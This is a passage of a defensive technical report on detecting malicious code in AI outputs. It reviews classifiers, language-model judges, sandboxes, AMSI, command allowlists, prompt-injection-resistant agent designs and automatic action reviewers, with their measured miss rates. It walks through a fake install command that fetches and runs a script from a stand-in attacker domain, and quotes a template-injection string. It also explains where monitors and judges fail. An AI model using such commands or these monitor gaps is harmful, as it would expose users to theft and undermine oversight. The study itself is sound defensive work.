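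Hashes are more useful for avoiding repeated work. Doutre and colleagues store the verdict on each package under its hash so that their system doesn't analyse the same package twice. This is sound for a package, because its contents determine its hash, but risky for the Acme command, because the script at the address can change while the command stays the same. The scanner should either let verdicts on commands that download something expire quickly or store them under the hash of the downloaded script.

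Domain reputations have a similar weakness. A newly registered domain has no history, which is mildly suspicious. An expired domain that a criminal has acquired may still have the good reputation its former owner earned.

### Where rules are the best choice

Rules work best when the defender can say exactly what to look for. When Push Security or Huntress publishes the address used in an attack, a defender can add it to a rule within minutes and search old responses for it. Training a new classifier would take longer and probably do no better on that address. Rules also work well for enforcing a policy, such as the sales dashboard's list of permitted SQL operations.

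Rules are also easy to audit, because a security team can read the download rule, see why it matched, and predict what a change will do. NeMo Guardrails returns the names of the rules that matched, so a developer whose weather script is removed can find out which rule matched it. It helps to store two test texts with each rule, one that it should match and a similar harmless one that it shouldn't, and to check the rule against both after every change.

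Rules can also flag code for closer inspection. Datadog recommends GuardDog as a first check before a language model investigates further, and the download rule would work well in the same role. A match could prompt the guardrail to check who controls the address and to download the script for inspection without running it, but it wouldn't justify blocking Acme's instructions.

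## Judging code with trained classifiers and language models

The download rule either matches a command or doesn't. A trained classifier gives every command a score, and the defender sets the minimum score at which the guardrail acts. A language-model judge reads the command and the text around it, then returns a verdict with reasons.

### Turning a command into a score

A classifier works with numbers, so it first splits the command into tokens, which are words, numbers and punctuation marks. In the simplest scheme, xᵢ is 1 if token i appears in the command and 0 if it doesn't. Training on labelled examples gives each token a weight wᵢ, which is positive if the token points towards malice and negative if it points away. A basic classifier called logistic regression adds up the weights and converts the sum into a score between 0 and 1:

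z = b + Σ wᵢxᵢ

score = 1 / (1 + e^(−z))

The constant b also comes from training.

The two Acme commands contain the same tokens, except that the criminal's also has a hyphen and the word "update". Their values of z therefore differ only by the weights of those two tokens. Since "update" is common in harmless commands, the classifier might score the criminal's command as safer.

Other classifiers use more information, such as counts of n-grams (short runs of neighbouring tokens) or embeddings. An embedding is a list of numbers that a neural network assigns to a text, so that texts with similar meanings get similar lists. *Living-Off-The-Land Command Detection Using Active Learning* (2021) scores each command together with the one that started it, because the pair can reveal an intention that neither shows alone.

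Order can matter too, since downloading a file and then running it is more suspicious than the reverse. *DONAPI* (2024), a detector for malicious npm packages, compared unordered sets of function calls with ordered sequences. For packages that bring in other malicious software, using sequences led to fewer false alarms but also two misses.

### Detection at very low false positive rates

Much of the research on commands concerns "living off the land", in which attackers misuse programs already on the machine. Companies run so many harmless commands that a classifier is useful only if it flags very few of them. The best studies therefore measure the detection rate at a fixed, tiny false positive rate.

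In *Robust Synthetic Data-Driven Detection of Living-Off-the-Land Reverse Shells*, Trizna, Demetrio and colleagues (2024) trained classifiers to detect reverse shells, which connect a victim's machine to an attacker and let the attacker type commands on it. They took harmless examples from about 50,000 Linux machines at one company. Real attack commands were scarce, so they wrote templates and filled them in with varied addresses, file names and other details to generate more. Their best model, a combination of 100 small decision trees, detected 99.94% of the attacks at a false positive rate of 1 in 100,000. The same kind of model detected 7.12% when trained without the generated variants, and published signature rules detected 3.37%.

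The 99.94% figure is probably too optimistic for real attacks. The researchers kept 30% of the templates for testing, but the test attacks came from the same generator as the training attacks. The test also had only about 235,000 harmless commands, so a rate of 1 in 100,000 amounts to two or three false alarms.

*SENTINEL* (Shoeb, Hasan and colleagues, 2026), a newer study of Windows commands, uses even less data, with 6,613 harmless commands and 436 malicious ones. At a false positive rate of 0.1%, its system detected 81.8% of the attacks, compared with 69.7% for BERT, an older language model trained on the same task. These percentages are consistent with 54 and 46 detections out of 66 test attacks, so the difference may be only eight commands. With roughly 1,000 harmless commands in the test set, a 0.1% false positive rate means one false alarm.

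The study is more valuable for showing that a high accuracy score can mislead. BERT classified 99.29% of the validation commands correctly, but a program that labelled every command harmless would have scored about 94%. Shoeb and colleagues then tested 50 commands from Volt Typhoon, a Chinese state-sponsored hacking campaign, and 50 harmless commands that used the same programs. BERT caught 58% of the attacks and SENTINEL caught 94%. SENTINEL also flagged 10% of the harmless commands, a hundred times the rate in the other test, presumably because they resembled attacks. A text guardrail will have to classify many harmless commands like these, including Acme's real install command.

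Classifiers can judge whole scripts as well. *Detecting Fileless Cryptojacking in PowerShell Using AST-Enhanced CodeBERT Models* (2026) combines syntax trees with CodeBERT, a language model for code, to find scripts that secretly mine cryptocurrency. It reports a high detection rate using a collection of 500 malicious scripts. That alone doesn't make a classifier suitable for a guardrail, because a program that flags every script would also detect all the malicious ones.

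### A classifier in use at Google

*Democratizing ML for Enterprise Security* (Momeni, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) describes a system that Google has used for several years. Each day, deliberately loose YARA rules reduce about 250 billion log events to 70,000 possible reverse shells, and a classifier reduces these to about five. After duplicates are removed, staff have to investigate about one every two days.

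The number is low partly because the team sets the threshold to match the number of alerts the staff can handle. Nobody inspects the billions of discarded events, so the system's detection rate in daily use is unknown.

The classifier is meant to make distinctions that would require constantly adjusting a rule. For example, Hydra is the name of both a password-cracking tool and a harmless Python library for configuring programs. A rule that looks for the name would flag both, and would also flag a user who only opens the tool's manual page.

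Momeni and colleagues tested three models on a year of real investigations, and the one using n-gram counts did as well as the two using different kinds of embeddings. They suggest that embedding a long command can obscure the few tokens that reveal an attack. The result is useful for anyone who has to check every response, because n-gram models are fast and need little compute.

Gemini 2.5 Flash, a Google language model, generated 10,000 malicious and 10,000 harmless commands for training in about 20 minutes. A classifier trained on them reached an F1 score of 0.95, compared with 0.88 for one trained on examples that an expert had spent several days collecting. Daily retraining on the results of investigations also helped. Over a year of commands, the retrained version found 53 attacks with 30 false alarms (64% precision), while a fixed version found 43 attacks with 107 false alarms (29%).

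An agent's terminal commands resemble the data in these studies, so the methods should transfer fairly well to tool calls. Chat responses contain far more tutorials and installation guides, so a classifier for them needs harmless examples of both.

### What a language-model judge receives and returns

The most detailed recent tests of language-model judges use agent skills. A skill is a folder containing a file, SKILL.md, with instructions that an agent follows to do a task. The folder may also contain scripts. Like chat responses, skills mix prose with code, but skills are usually much longer. Public websites called skill hubs distribute them, and some scan them for malware.

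*Demystifying Detectors Guarding Agent Skill Hubs* (Yang, Ying and colleagues, 2026) compares six detectors, four of which can use a language model. Cisco's skill-scanner puts the skill's contents into one prompt and asks for a list of findings, each with a threat category, a severity and an explanation. Ordinary code then blocks the skill if any finding has high or critical severity. NVIDIA's skillspector uses three specialised prompts, then asks the model to review the findings and discard any it can't confirm. Tencent's AI-Infra-Guard is an agent that explores the files, audits the code and reviews its own findings.

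The fourth, skill-vetter, is itself a skill. It contains instructions for a coding agent to inspect every file for warning signs and decide whether the requested permissions fit the skill's stated purpose. The agent returns a report with a risk level and a verdict. In the test, the agent could read and search files but couldn't use the web or run code.

Yang and colleagues tested these detectors with Qwen3.6, DeepSeek-V4 and GPT-5.4 on 886 malicious and 591 harmless skills from seven datasets. They kept the original labels for artificial skills and checked the labels of skills from public hubs by hand. These are some of the results, with costs estimated from API prices:

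| Detector | Model | Malicious skills detected | Harmless skills flagged | Seconds per skill | Cost per skill |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| skill-scanner | None, rules only | 36.1% | 12.0% | 4.0 | None |
| skill-scanner | Qwen3.6 | 95.1% | 17.8% | 69.3 | $0.0004 |
| skill-scanner | GPT-5.4 | 88.1% | 16.6% | 21.6 | $0.031 |
| skillspector | None, rules only | 52.0% | 17.3% | 1.0 | None |
| skillspector | GPT-5.4 | 94.2% | 22.2% | 20.5 | $0.162 |
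| skill-vetter | Qwen3.6 | 93.0% | 6.3% | 77.8 | $0.001 |
| skill-vetter | DeepSeek-V4 | 92.4% | 7.1% | 137.3 | $0.007 |
| skill-vetter | GPT-5.4 | 94.6% | 30.8% | 69.7 | $0.506 |
| AI-Infra-Guard | GPT-5.4 | 86.1% | 8.5% | 109.5 | $0.553 |

Adding a language model greatly improved detection over rules alone, but more expensive models weren't reliably better. Skill-vetter cost over 400 times as much with GPT-5.4 as with Qwen3.6 and flagged nearly five times as many harmless skills.

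Even the fastest judge took about 20 seconds, which is acceptable before installing a skill but too long for most chat users. Checking a short response should take less time and money than checking a folder of files. If cost is proportional to length, checking a million responses of 1,000 tokens each would cost about $3,700 with skill-scanner's GPT-5.4 setup and $35 with its Qwen3.6 setup. These are rough estimates, because generated text usually costs more than input. Screening with a cheap rule or classifier first, as Google does, would lower the total.

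### Install commands cause errors in both directions

Yang and colleagues examined 2,790 findings behind the false alarms. The largest group, 36%, concerned access to passwords, keys or local data. One skill for making phone calls was blocked because it sent its access key to the company that issued it, which is the normal way to log in to such a service.

Another 9% concerned software installation. In one case, skillspector flagged the official install command for SDKMAN, a tool for managing programming software, because someone might compromise the download source, a risk that applies to any download. Yang and colleagues conclude that it is hard to judge a setup command without inspecting the code it installs.

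Judges also let malicious skills through. Across the three models, skill-vetter did so 177 times, and in 151 of those cases it had identified the harmful part in its report. In 92 cases it let the skill through because the files contained no executable code for the malicious instructions. Some of those instructions told users to run a script from elsewhere. In another case, it advised removing a hook that downloaded and ran unverified code, but didn't block the skill.

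A judge could easily block the real Acme command because the download could be dangerous, or allow the criminal's because the response itself contains no malware. It would help to let the judge answer "unknown" when the important code is outside the response. The guardrail could then fetch the script for inspection or ask a person.

Better instructions can reduce these errors. Yang and colleagues revised skill-vetter's prompt to address the causes they had found, and tested it on new skills from MalSkillBench, one of the seven datasets. With GPT-5.4, false positives fell from an average of 66 to 9 out of 150 harmless skills, and misses fell from 11 to 6 out of 150 malicious ones. GPT-5.4's high false positive rate in the main test therefore came largely from the prompt.

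### Malicious tools for agents

Agents also install tools from public collections. *MalTool* (Hu, Jia and colleagues, 2026) tested scanners on 7,027 malicious tools. Of these, 1,300 were small programs that a language model had written, and the rest were real tools with such code added. The researchers had run the generated programs in a controlled environment to confirm that they worked as intended, which makes the labels unusually reliable. The harmless set had 4,846 tools from 1,147 code repositories.

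Three of the scanners use language models. Tencent's scanner flagged about 38% of the harmless repositories and missed 59% of the small malicious programs. Cisco's flagged only seven harmless repositories, or 0.6%, but missed about 70% of the small programs. It caught 93% of the programs that downloaded other software but none of those that inserted false records into an agent's database, probably because such insertions look like ordinary database code.

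Combining the scanners did not solve the problem. When Hu and colleagues counted a tool as malicious if any of the six scanners flagged it, accuracy was 81.4%. Flagging everything would have scored higher, at 86%, because the test had many more malicious tools than harmless repositories. The combination flagged about two thirds of the harmless repositories.

### Comparing a description with the code

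A database insertion is suspicious in a tool described as only reporting the weather. To find such mismatches, Shi, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Description-Code Inconsistency in Real-world MCP Servers*, developed a checker that compares a tool's description with what its code does. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is a common standard for connecting models to tools. The model chooses a tool by its description and normally never sees the code.

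Shi and colleagues call a tool inconsistent if

F_claimed ≠ F_actual, or E_actual ⊄ E_claimed

F is the tool's main function and E is the set of its side effects. The first condition covers a tool that is described as searching for files but deletes them. The second covers a tool that searches for files as described but also uploads the search terms to a server, which its description omits.

The checker collects the tool's description, its main code and the helper functions that the code uses. It then asks a language model whether the description matches the code and, in a separate prompt, asks the model to look for mismatches, because the wording of a question can bias the answer. If the answers conflict, the checker uses a third prompt to have the model compare the reasons and decide.

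The checker found inconsistencies in 9.93% of 19,200 tools. That is far too many for all of them to be malicious, and some descriptions were probably just out of date. The percentage also includes the language model's mistakes in judgement.

In the Acme response, the claimed function is to install Acme, and the command's visible function is to download a script and run it. Both versions look consistent until the guardrail fetches the script. Suppose the criminal's script installs Acme and also uploads the browser's saved passwords. Comparing the main functions would miss the upload, which is an undeclared side effect. Acme's own script might also have one, such as changing a settings file so that the shell can find the new program. A useful checker would have to treat the password upload as serious and the settings change as routine.

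In Yang and colleagues' results, mismatches between a skill's description and behaviour accounted for 12% of the findings behind false alarms. Over half of those came from skillspector, which has a prompt for comparing the two. In 43% of the mismatch findings, the mismatch was real but didn't show malice, for example because the skill's author had exaggerated what it could do. In 39%, the claim of a mismatch was wrong or poorly supported. The comparison is useful for deciding what to inspect, but a mismatch alone is a poor reason to block a skill.

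### The same operation as code and as prose

A guardrail for text should recognise a harmful operation whether someone writes it as a command or describes it in English. *RedCode* (Guo, Liu and colleagues, 2024) tested this by checking whether agents refused, rather than by using a separate detector. It includes 750 risky operations in Python and 600 in Bash, a common shell language. Each is also written as a short summary in English and as a detailed description of the steps, giving 4,050 test cases in total.

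The agents worked in isolated containers, and scripts checked whether they had carried out each task, for example by looking for an important system file that the agent had been asked to delete. Agents generally refused less often, and carried out the harmful operation more often, when the request was in English than when it was in code. The detailed descriptions succeeded more often than the summaries, probably because they gave clearer instructions. Agents also refused Bash less often than Python.

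RedCode tested models from 2024 and earlier, such as Claude 3.5 and GPT-4, so its refusal rates are weak evidence about current agents. Many of its operations are also examples of insecure code, which agents have less reason to refuse. But its design is well suited to testing a guardrail, because it presents the same operation in different formats. A defender could submit the criminal's Acme command, then an English sentence telling an agent to download and run the same script. If the guardrail flags only the command, its detection depends on the format.

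Newer results suggest that language models have made detectors less dependent on format. In one of Yang and colleagues' datasets, where the attacks are mostly in plain language, rules alone caught 7.5% of them with skill-scanner and 11.8% with skillspector. Adding Qwen3.6 raised these figures to 96.8% and 64.5%. However, this isn't a paired experiment like RedCode, and judges can still give format too much weight. For example, skill-vetter tends to treat instructions without executable code as harmless.

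### Test data that resembles the training data

A common objection to good scores is that the test samples are too similar to the training samples. In *MaliciousSkillBench*, Wang, Liu and colleagues (2026) measured how much this similarity affects scores. They combined skills from 13 public sources, removed duplicates and kept 7,505 malicious and 2,235 harmless ones. They then trained simple classifiers on word frequencies.

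When the skills were split at random, the best classifier flagged 9.4% of the harmless test skills. When it was tested on sources it had never seen, it flagged 62.4% of the harmless skills (340 of 545). It still caught 95.6% of the malicious skills, so the detection rate alone would not have revealed the problem. The classifier had apparently learned to treat unfamiliar writing as malicious. Most of the false alarms came from one source, so the false alarm rate could be very different with another selection of sources.

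Training the classifier on a more balanced mixture of data lowered its false positive rate on new sources to 43.3%, which is still far too high. A more promising approach is to train on harmless text from the application the guardrail will protect and keep updating it, as Google does. The final test should use data from a different source or a later period.

Language-model judges don't need training on these datasets, but their results also vary from one dataset to another. Yang and colleagues tested skill-vetter on another benchmark, which has 154 malicious skills. With Qwen3.6, it missed an average of 109 (71%), compared with only 7% in the main test. The revised prompt didn't help Qwen3.6 on this benchmark, but it reduced GPT-5.4's misses from 52 to 32.

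Wrong labels add to the uncertainty. *Do Not Mention This to the User* (2026) provided the first large labelled collection of malicious skills from public hubs, but Yang and colleagues confirmed only 95 of its 157 malicious labels. Wang and colleagues found 34 skills that some sources had labelled malicious and others harmless. Researchers often check harmless labels less carefully. *The Devil Wears Markdown* (2026) uses 300 supposedly harmless skills and reports that its researchers did not independently check 200 of them. *MalSkillBench* (2026) checks malicious labels more thoroughly, by verifying the behaviour of its 3,944 malicious skills at runtime.

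### Unstable verdicts and prompt injection

A language model can give different answers to the same question. Yang and colleagues ran each judge three times with Qwen3.6. AI-Infra-Guard changed its verdict at least once for 64.3% of the skills from *Do Not Mention This to the User*, skillspector for 57.4%, skill-vetter for 33.3% and skill-scanner for 16.3%. Most of this variation did not show in the overall scores, because errors in one run tended to cancel out errors in another.

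These cases were unusually hard because all the harmless skills in that set had originally been labelled malicious, so they looked suspicious. On an easier dataset, skill-vetter changed its verdict for only 2.5% of the skills. Still, developers will reasonably lose trust in a guardrail that passes their code one day and fails the same code the next.

One remedy is to ask three times and take the majority verdict. If each run is wrong with probability p and the errors are independent, the majority is wrong with probability

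3p²(1 − p) + p³

If each run of the judge has a 10% chance of error and the errors are independent, a majority vote of three runs is wrong 2.8% of the time. The real improvement will usually be smaller, because a model tends to repeat its mistakes, and voting can't help with a case on which the judge is right only half the time. Voting also triples the cost. Sending split verdicts to a person may be a better use of the extra runs.

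A judge is also open to prompt injection, and Sandle (2026) reports in *AI security tools can be manipulated into running malware, researchers warn* that manipulation can even lead such tools to run the malware. A defender can limit the damage by giving the judge no way to run code, no access to passwords, and no ability to overrule fixed checks. In skill-scanner, for example, the language model can add findings or raise their severity, but it can't remove a finding that came from a rule. The drawback is that it can't correct the rules' false alarms.

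## Testing code in a sandbox and checking it as it runs

Once a shell runs the Acme command, the script from the address is on the machine, where software can inspect it and watch its effects. A defender can use what the code does to decide whether it is malicious, or can restrict what any code can do without having to make that decision.

### Running a snippet to see what it does

A sandbox test runs suspect code on a disposable machine, usually a virtual one. For a snippet from a chat response, it has five steps:

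1. Choose an interpreter that matches the snippet's language and, if possible, its version.
2. Supply what the snippet needs, such as packages, files and values for undefined variables. Decoy passwords in the browser's folder give a password stealer something to take.
3. Run the snippet with a time limit.
4. Record its actions, including the files it reads or changes, the programs it starts and the servers it contacts.
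5. Compare the actions with a set of rules, reach a verdict and discard the machine.

If the sandbox has internet access, this test can tell the two Acme commands apart. Acme's script installs a program, while the criminal's also reads the decoy passwords and sends them over the internet. But the criminal's server can deliver a different script next time, so the application should install the copy it tested instead of downloading another.

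### Snippets that can't run

Most snippets are harder to test than the Acme command. *SelfPiCo* (Xue, Hu and colleagues, 2024) reports that 75% can't run directly, because so many lack definitions or packages. If Python runs the line `requests.post(address, data=payload)` on its own, it stops with an error because nothing defines `requests`, `address` or `payload`. The sandbox records no harmful action, and a careless rule would classify the snippet as harmless.

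A language model can fill in the missing parts of a snippet so that it runs. In *Treefix*, Souza and Pradel (2025) first list the snippet's undefined names and ask a model for a few lines of code that define them. They then run the snippet with those lines in front. If it fails, the model gets the error message and tries again. The model then writes further versions of the added lines to reach any code that hasn't run yet, since one run can't follow both branches of an "if" statement.

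This method executed 84% of the lines in functions from open-source projects and 82% of those in Stack Overflow snippets. Xue and colleagues' similar tool executed 72.7% and 83.3%, respectively, in their own test. In Souza and Pradel's comparison, neither that tool nor any other rival executed more than about 77% of the lines in the Stack Overflow snippets, so the percentages evidently depend on the set-up.

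Both teams built their tools for debugging and program analysis, and neither team's results show how well the tools reveal malware. The invented values are a serious weakness for detecting it. If the model sets `payload` to "hello", the sandbox records a harmless greeting, though the original program might have put stolen passwords there. The lines that never ran could also contain the harmful part. A clean result for a fragment is therefore weak evidence that the whole program is safe. A harmful action is strong evidence that the program is unsafe, provided the action doesn't depend on invented values.

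### Delay and late effects

*MLRan* (2025), a paper on ransomware, recommends limiting runs to two minutes, citing a study by Küchler and colleagues in which 98% of the blocks of code that ran did so within that time. Recording a program's actions slows it down. In *Decoding the Secrets of Machine Learning in Malware Classification* (2023), malware samples took 125% longer on average with recording on. At that rate, a two-minute run would take four and a half minutes, and the researchers allowed five.

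Few chat users would wait that long. Testing a million responses a day at two minutes each would keep almost 1,400 sandboxes busy around the clock. Many snippets would finish in seconds, but the test still makes more sense for packages and agent skills, because their installation can wait a few minutes.

Some code does nothing harmful until a certain date, or until a person has opened a few files. *MLRan* recommends simulating a user's activity and varying the length of the run. A sandbox can also record preparations for later harm, such as a new scheduled task or a change to a file that the shell reads at every login. Genuine installers also change these login files, so the rules need to be based on what the added line does.

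*Decoding the Secrets of Machine Learning in Malware Classification* counted a sample as having run properly only if it made at least 50 calls to Windows functions. A snippet that deletes a folder may need only one or two. A sandbox for snippets therefore needs another way to tell whether the code ran properly, such as checking whether it reached its last line, and should report "not tested" when it didn't.

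### Scanning a script just before it runs

The Antimalware Scan Interface (AMSI) in Windows lets programs that run scripts, such as PowerShell, send them to the machine's antivirus product for checking just before they run. According to Microsoft's *How the Antimalware Scan Interface (AMSI) helps you defend against malware*, PowerShell submits the text of a script through AMSI when the script is ready to execute, and runs it only if the antivirus product's verdict allows it. Any code the script generates while running goes through the same check. AMSI only delivers the text, so detection depends on the antivirus product's rules and classifiers.

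Checking code as it runs helps when an agent runs a script that it wrote to a file earlier, because the command alone shows little of the code. *AMSI-Based Detection of Malicious PowerShell Code Using Contextual Embeddings* (Hendler, Kels and Rubin, 2019) compared a week of AMSI records with a week of logged PowerShell commands at one large company. The command log was missing most of the code. More than 8% of the AMSI records were at least 16,000 characters long, compared with under 0.0008% of the commands, and the word "function" appeared in 39% of the AMSI records and 0.14% of the commands.

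Microsoft Office uses AMSI differently for macros, which are small programs inside documents. Office logs a macro's calls to system functions and the data it passes to them. When the macro makes a call that Office considers high-risk, Office pauses the macro and submits the log. The macro continues only if the verdict is favourable. This is a monitor that checks both the macro's behaviour so far and its next step.

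AMSI's coverage includes PowerShell, VBScript, Microsoft's version of JavaScript and programs for newer versions of .NET, so it might catch the C# code that Honestcue receives from Gemini and runs in memory. However, Microsoft says AMSI doesn't support Python or Perl, and it isn't available for the Mac and Linux shells where people would normally run the Acme command. Any Windows application can submit text to AMSI, including a chat program that wants to check messages before displaying them. But if nothing has run yet, the antivirus product receives only the message, not the script, which is still on the server.

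Antivirus products can also watch a program's behaviour after it starts, but text/plain's *Defensive Technology* (2024) points out that this may detect the harm too late. AMSI gives these products a chance to stop a script before it does anything.

### Results for detectors that use AMSI

Hendler and colleagues trained classifiers on PowerShell code that AMSI had recorded from May to July 2018 and tested them on code from the next three months. The test set had 1,329 malicious and 8,807 harmless items after they removed near-duplicates. At a false positive rate of no more than 0.1%, the best classifier detected 89.4% of the malicious code. A simpler classifier that counted single tokens and pairs of neighbouring tokens detected 64.3%.

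Those two classifiers had the same AUC, 0.994, on data from the training period, so the AUC did not show a large practical difference between them. The simpler one also did almost as well on that data at the 0.1% limit, detecting 89.8% against 92.9%, but its performance declined much faster over time. Daily retraining, as at Google, should help.

The malicious code behind the 89.4% figure came from a sandbox and the harmless code from ordinary office machines, so the classifier may have learned differences between the two environments. Hendler and colleagues also didn't test the same attacks using only command logs, so it's unclear how much AMSI contributed to detection. Still, the company that supplied the data has used the detector in its own product since April 2019, which suggests that the false alarms were tolerable.

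*MPSD* describes another defence that intercepts PowerShell scripts through AMSI, and reports that it missed 1.83% of malicious scripts. This figure is comparable with Hendler and colleagues' 10.6% only if both systems have the same false-alarm rate.

### Keeping data from becoming commands

Some protections work without anyone deciding whether a text is malicious. In a parameterised query, the application sends the database a command with gaps in it and supplies the values separately:

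`UPDATE Customers SET City=? WHERE CustomerID=?`

The database parses the command before it uses the values. If the first value contains SQL, the database stores it as text in the customer's city field instead of running it. The second value must match a customer's number, so the query can't change every record at once. It can still change the wrong customer's record or store a city that doesn't exist.

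A sales dashboard could keep a set of such queries and have the model select one and fill in the values, so the model would write no SQL. However, staff could ask only the questions that the developers had planned for. Table and column names also can't be filled in as values, so each variation in table or column needs its own query.

Output encoding does the same job for a web page, for example by replacing each `<` in a response with `&lt;`. The encoding has to suit the destination, though. Braces have no special meaning in HTML, so HTML encoding leaves `{{7*7}}` unchanged. A template engine that receives it can still evaluate it to 49.

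### Lists of allowed commands

A coding agent has to run commands, so its owner may instead list the ones it can run without permission. This works when the entries are narrow. OpenAI recommends entries such as `cargo test`, which runs a project's tests, and advises against allowing everything that starts with `python` or `curl`. An entry for `python` would allow the agent to run any Python program, and an entry for `curl` would let it contact either Acme address.

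Many users ignore that advice. Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues (2026), in *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight*, found that a sizeable minority of OpenAI's internal users allowed every command beginning with `python`. According to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), about half of the active users of Claude Code's terminal version had written a rule allowing some shell commands. Anthropic reports that 5% allow any command and another 43% allow interpreters such as Python, which it considers nearly equivalent.

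Even a command that looks narrow can do more than search for files, as `find` does when it runs a program on each file it finds. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) recommends giving the agent a purpose-built tool that can only search. Cursor, which makes a code editor with a built-in agent, chose a sandbox without network access over a very detailed list of commands (*Agent Sandboxing*).

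### Agents that outside text can't direct

The malicious package in the AGENTS.md case was dangerous because text from outside determined the agent's next action. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues argue that once an agent has read untrusted text, it should be impossible for that text to trigger any action with harmful consequences. They describe six designs that restrict agents in this way:

| Design | How it works | What it costs or leaves open |
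|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The model picks from a fixed list of actions and never sees the results | Requests that nobody planned for fail |
| Plan, then execute | The agent settles its list of tool calls before reading outside text | Outside text can still change what goes into a call, such as the body of an email |
| Map-reduce | A separate model without tools reads each document and gives a restricted answer, such as yes or no | A hostile document can still cause a wrong answer about itself |
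| Two models | One model plans and uses tools, and another without tools reads outside text. Ordinary software passes on the results without showing them to the first | The results themselves may be false or harmful |
| Code, then execute | The model writes a complete program before any outside data arrives | The data can still corrupt the program's output |
| Reduced context | The system removes the user's prompt before the model writes its final answer | The answer may overlook details of the request |

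For a system like the sales dashboard, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest that the model write the query and the Python code for analysing the results, but never read the results. An instruction that a customer typed into an address field would then never reach the model. But the model also couldn't tell if a query had returned the wrong data, so it wouldn't know to try another. The Python code should still run in a sandbox, because a malicious user could ask for harmful code directly.

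A coding agent loses more. In the safest version they consider, a model without tools reads outside documentation and reduces it to a strict list of functions, with names limited to, say, 30 characters. Very few malicious instructions would survive this, but the agent also wouldn't see the explanations or sample code that programmers rely on heavily.

These designs offer firmer protection than a classifier because they don't depend on recognising an attack. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues argue for them using ten example applications, but don't measure how much useful work the restricted agents still complete. The designs seem to suit an agent with one well-defined job, but not a general coding assistant.

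### The install command in a sandbox

NVIDIA warns that coding agents normally run commands with all of the user's permissions. A sandbox around the agent's terminal removes most of those permissions. The code editor Zed by default stops its agent's terminal from contacting the network or writing outside the project's folders. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* describes Claude Code's sandbox, which allows network connections only through a proxy, a program outside the sandbox that checks each domain against a list.

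Suppose an agent in such a sandbox runs the command with the criminal's address:

1. The shell starts `curl` and `sh`, and connects the output of the first to the second.
2. `curl` asks the proxy for a connection to `acme-update.example`.
3. The domain isn't on the list, so the proxy holds the request and asks the user.
4. If the user refuses, `curl` reports an error and passes nothing on. `sh` has no script to run.

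Acme's own command goes through the same steps if its domain isn't on the list. The sandbox stops the unknown download without determining which address is genuine, and leaves that decision to a person who may not know either. If Acme's domain is on the list but has since lapsed and passed to a criminal, the download goes ahead without anyone being asked to approve it.

Now suppose the user approves the criminal's address. The script runs, but it can't change files outside the project folder, so it can't replace system programs. Depending on the settings, it may still be able to read private files elsewhere, which it can then send to the approved address. Anthropic stresses that a sandbox has to restrict both files and network connections. Otherwise, a program can send any secrets it reads over the network, or tamper with system files until it escapes the sandbox.

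Acme's genuine installer would probably fail too, since it has to put a program where the rest of the system can find it. The user would have to let it run outside the sandbox. A sandbox therefore gives little lasting protection when installing new software, unless the user wants the tool only inside the sandbox.

Sandboxing also disrupts ordinary work. Betts, Gaitonde and Haugland report in *Implementing a secure sandbox for local agents* that many commands need unexpected permissions, even for basic tests and builds. Cursor's agent often retried a blocked command without asking for more access, until the team changed the error messages to name the restriction that had blocked it. The team rejected virtual machines on Macs because they started slowly and used a lot of memory.

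### How often people have to approve

Sandboxes reduce interruptions. Anthropic counted 84% fewer permission requests in its own use, and Betts and colleagues report that sandboxed agents stop 40% less often. These figures aren't comparable, because the products require permission for different things even without a sandbox.

The remaining requests can go to an automatic reviewer. Trębacz and colleagues give an illustrative breakdown of 10,000 actions by Codex inside OpenAI. Of these, 9,280 stayed within the sandbox. A separate agent reviewed the other 720 and refused seven. Codex found a safer way to continue in four of those cases and stopped to ask the user in three. Without the reviewer, a person would have had to answer all 720 requests.

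Anthropic's reviewer for Claude Code, called auto mode, is a language model that sees the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's explanations or any text that the tools return. A malicious web page therefore can't address the reviewer directly. A quick first check errs towards blocking, and a slower one re-examines whatever the first flags. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* gives these error rates:

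| | Harmless actions blocked (10,000 real tool calls) | Dangerous actions missed (52 real cases) | Attempts to send out data missed (1,000 artificial cases) |
|---|---|---|---|
| First check alone | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
| Both checks | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

The second check prevents about 810 wrong refusals per 10,000 actions, but it also lets more dangerous actions through. The test had only 52 real cases, so the true miss rate could plausibly be from 9% to 30%. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the reviewer identified the danger but wrongly treated the user as having agreed to it. The cases mostly involve an agent doing more than the user wanted, such as deleting shared work, so the rates are weak evidence of how well the checks detect malware.

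An outside test produced much worse results. *Measuring the Permission Gate* used 128 deliberately ambiguous requests, such as one to clean up a project's branches without saying which ones. According to BestHub's *Can Claude Code’s Auto Mode Replace Human Review?*, the system missed 115 of 142 dangerous actions (81%) and blocked 22 of 111 harmless ones (20%). The published percentages imply that 51 of the misses never reached the reviewer, largely because auto mode allows edits inside the project folder without a review. The results therefore depend heavily on which actions are reviewed. Ordinary requests are usually clearer than the test's, and a language model did most of the labelling.

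Anthropic has since strengthened the reviewer and reports that its miss rate on artificial attacks created by Apollo Research, an AI safety company, fell from 12% to 7%. In another test that Anthropic commissioned, none of the 720 prompt injections attempted against each of three Claude models in auto mode succeeded. Only 0.09% succeeded on average without auto mode, so most of the protection came from the models themselves. The same test's results for Codex with GPT-5.6 Sol are better evidence that reviewers help, because OpenAI's reviewer cut successful attacks from 19% to 5.8%.

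### Approving out of habit

People are a weak alternative to these reviewers. Claude Code users approve 97% of permission requests, but most requests are probably harmless, so that figure alone doesn't prove carelessness. Anthropic therefore had 1,053 paid testers do coding work and replaced one request in each session with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it, while auto mode blocked 89% of the same commands. Testers refused about 17% of the dangerous commands that appeared early in a session and about 5% of those that appeared after 50 or more requests.

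The testers worked in a test environment with nothing of their own at risk, so developers would probably be more careful with their own projects. Anthropic also has a commercial reason to favour fewer interruptions. Even so, the gap is so large that a guardrail shouldn't depend on a person's click as a check, particularly late in a long session. Anthropic still recommends that users review the actions themselves for important changes to live systems.

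People may pay more attention to each request if they get fewer of them. They also seem to respond better to broader questions. Claude Code users reject 39% of the plans the agent proposes, compared with 3% of individual actions. For the Acme command, asking "Do you trust acme-update.example, which you have never used before?" would be more useful than asking whether to run a line of shell.

### Harm from permitted actions

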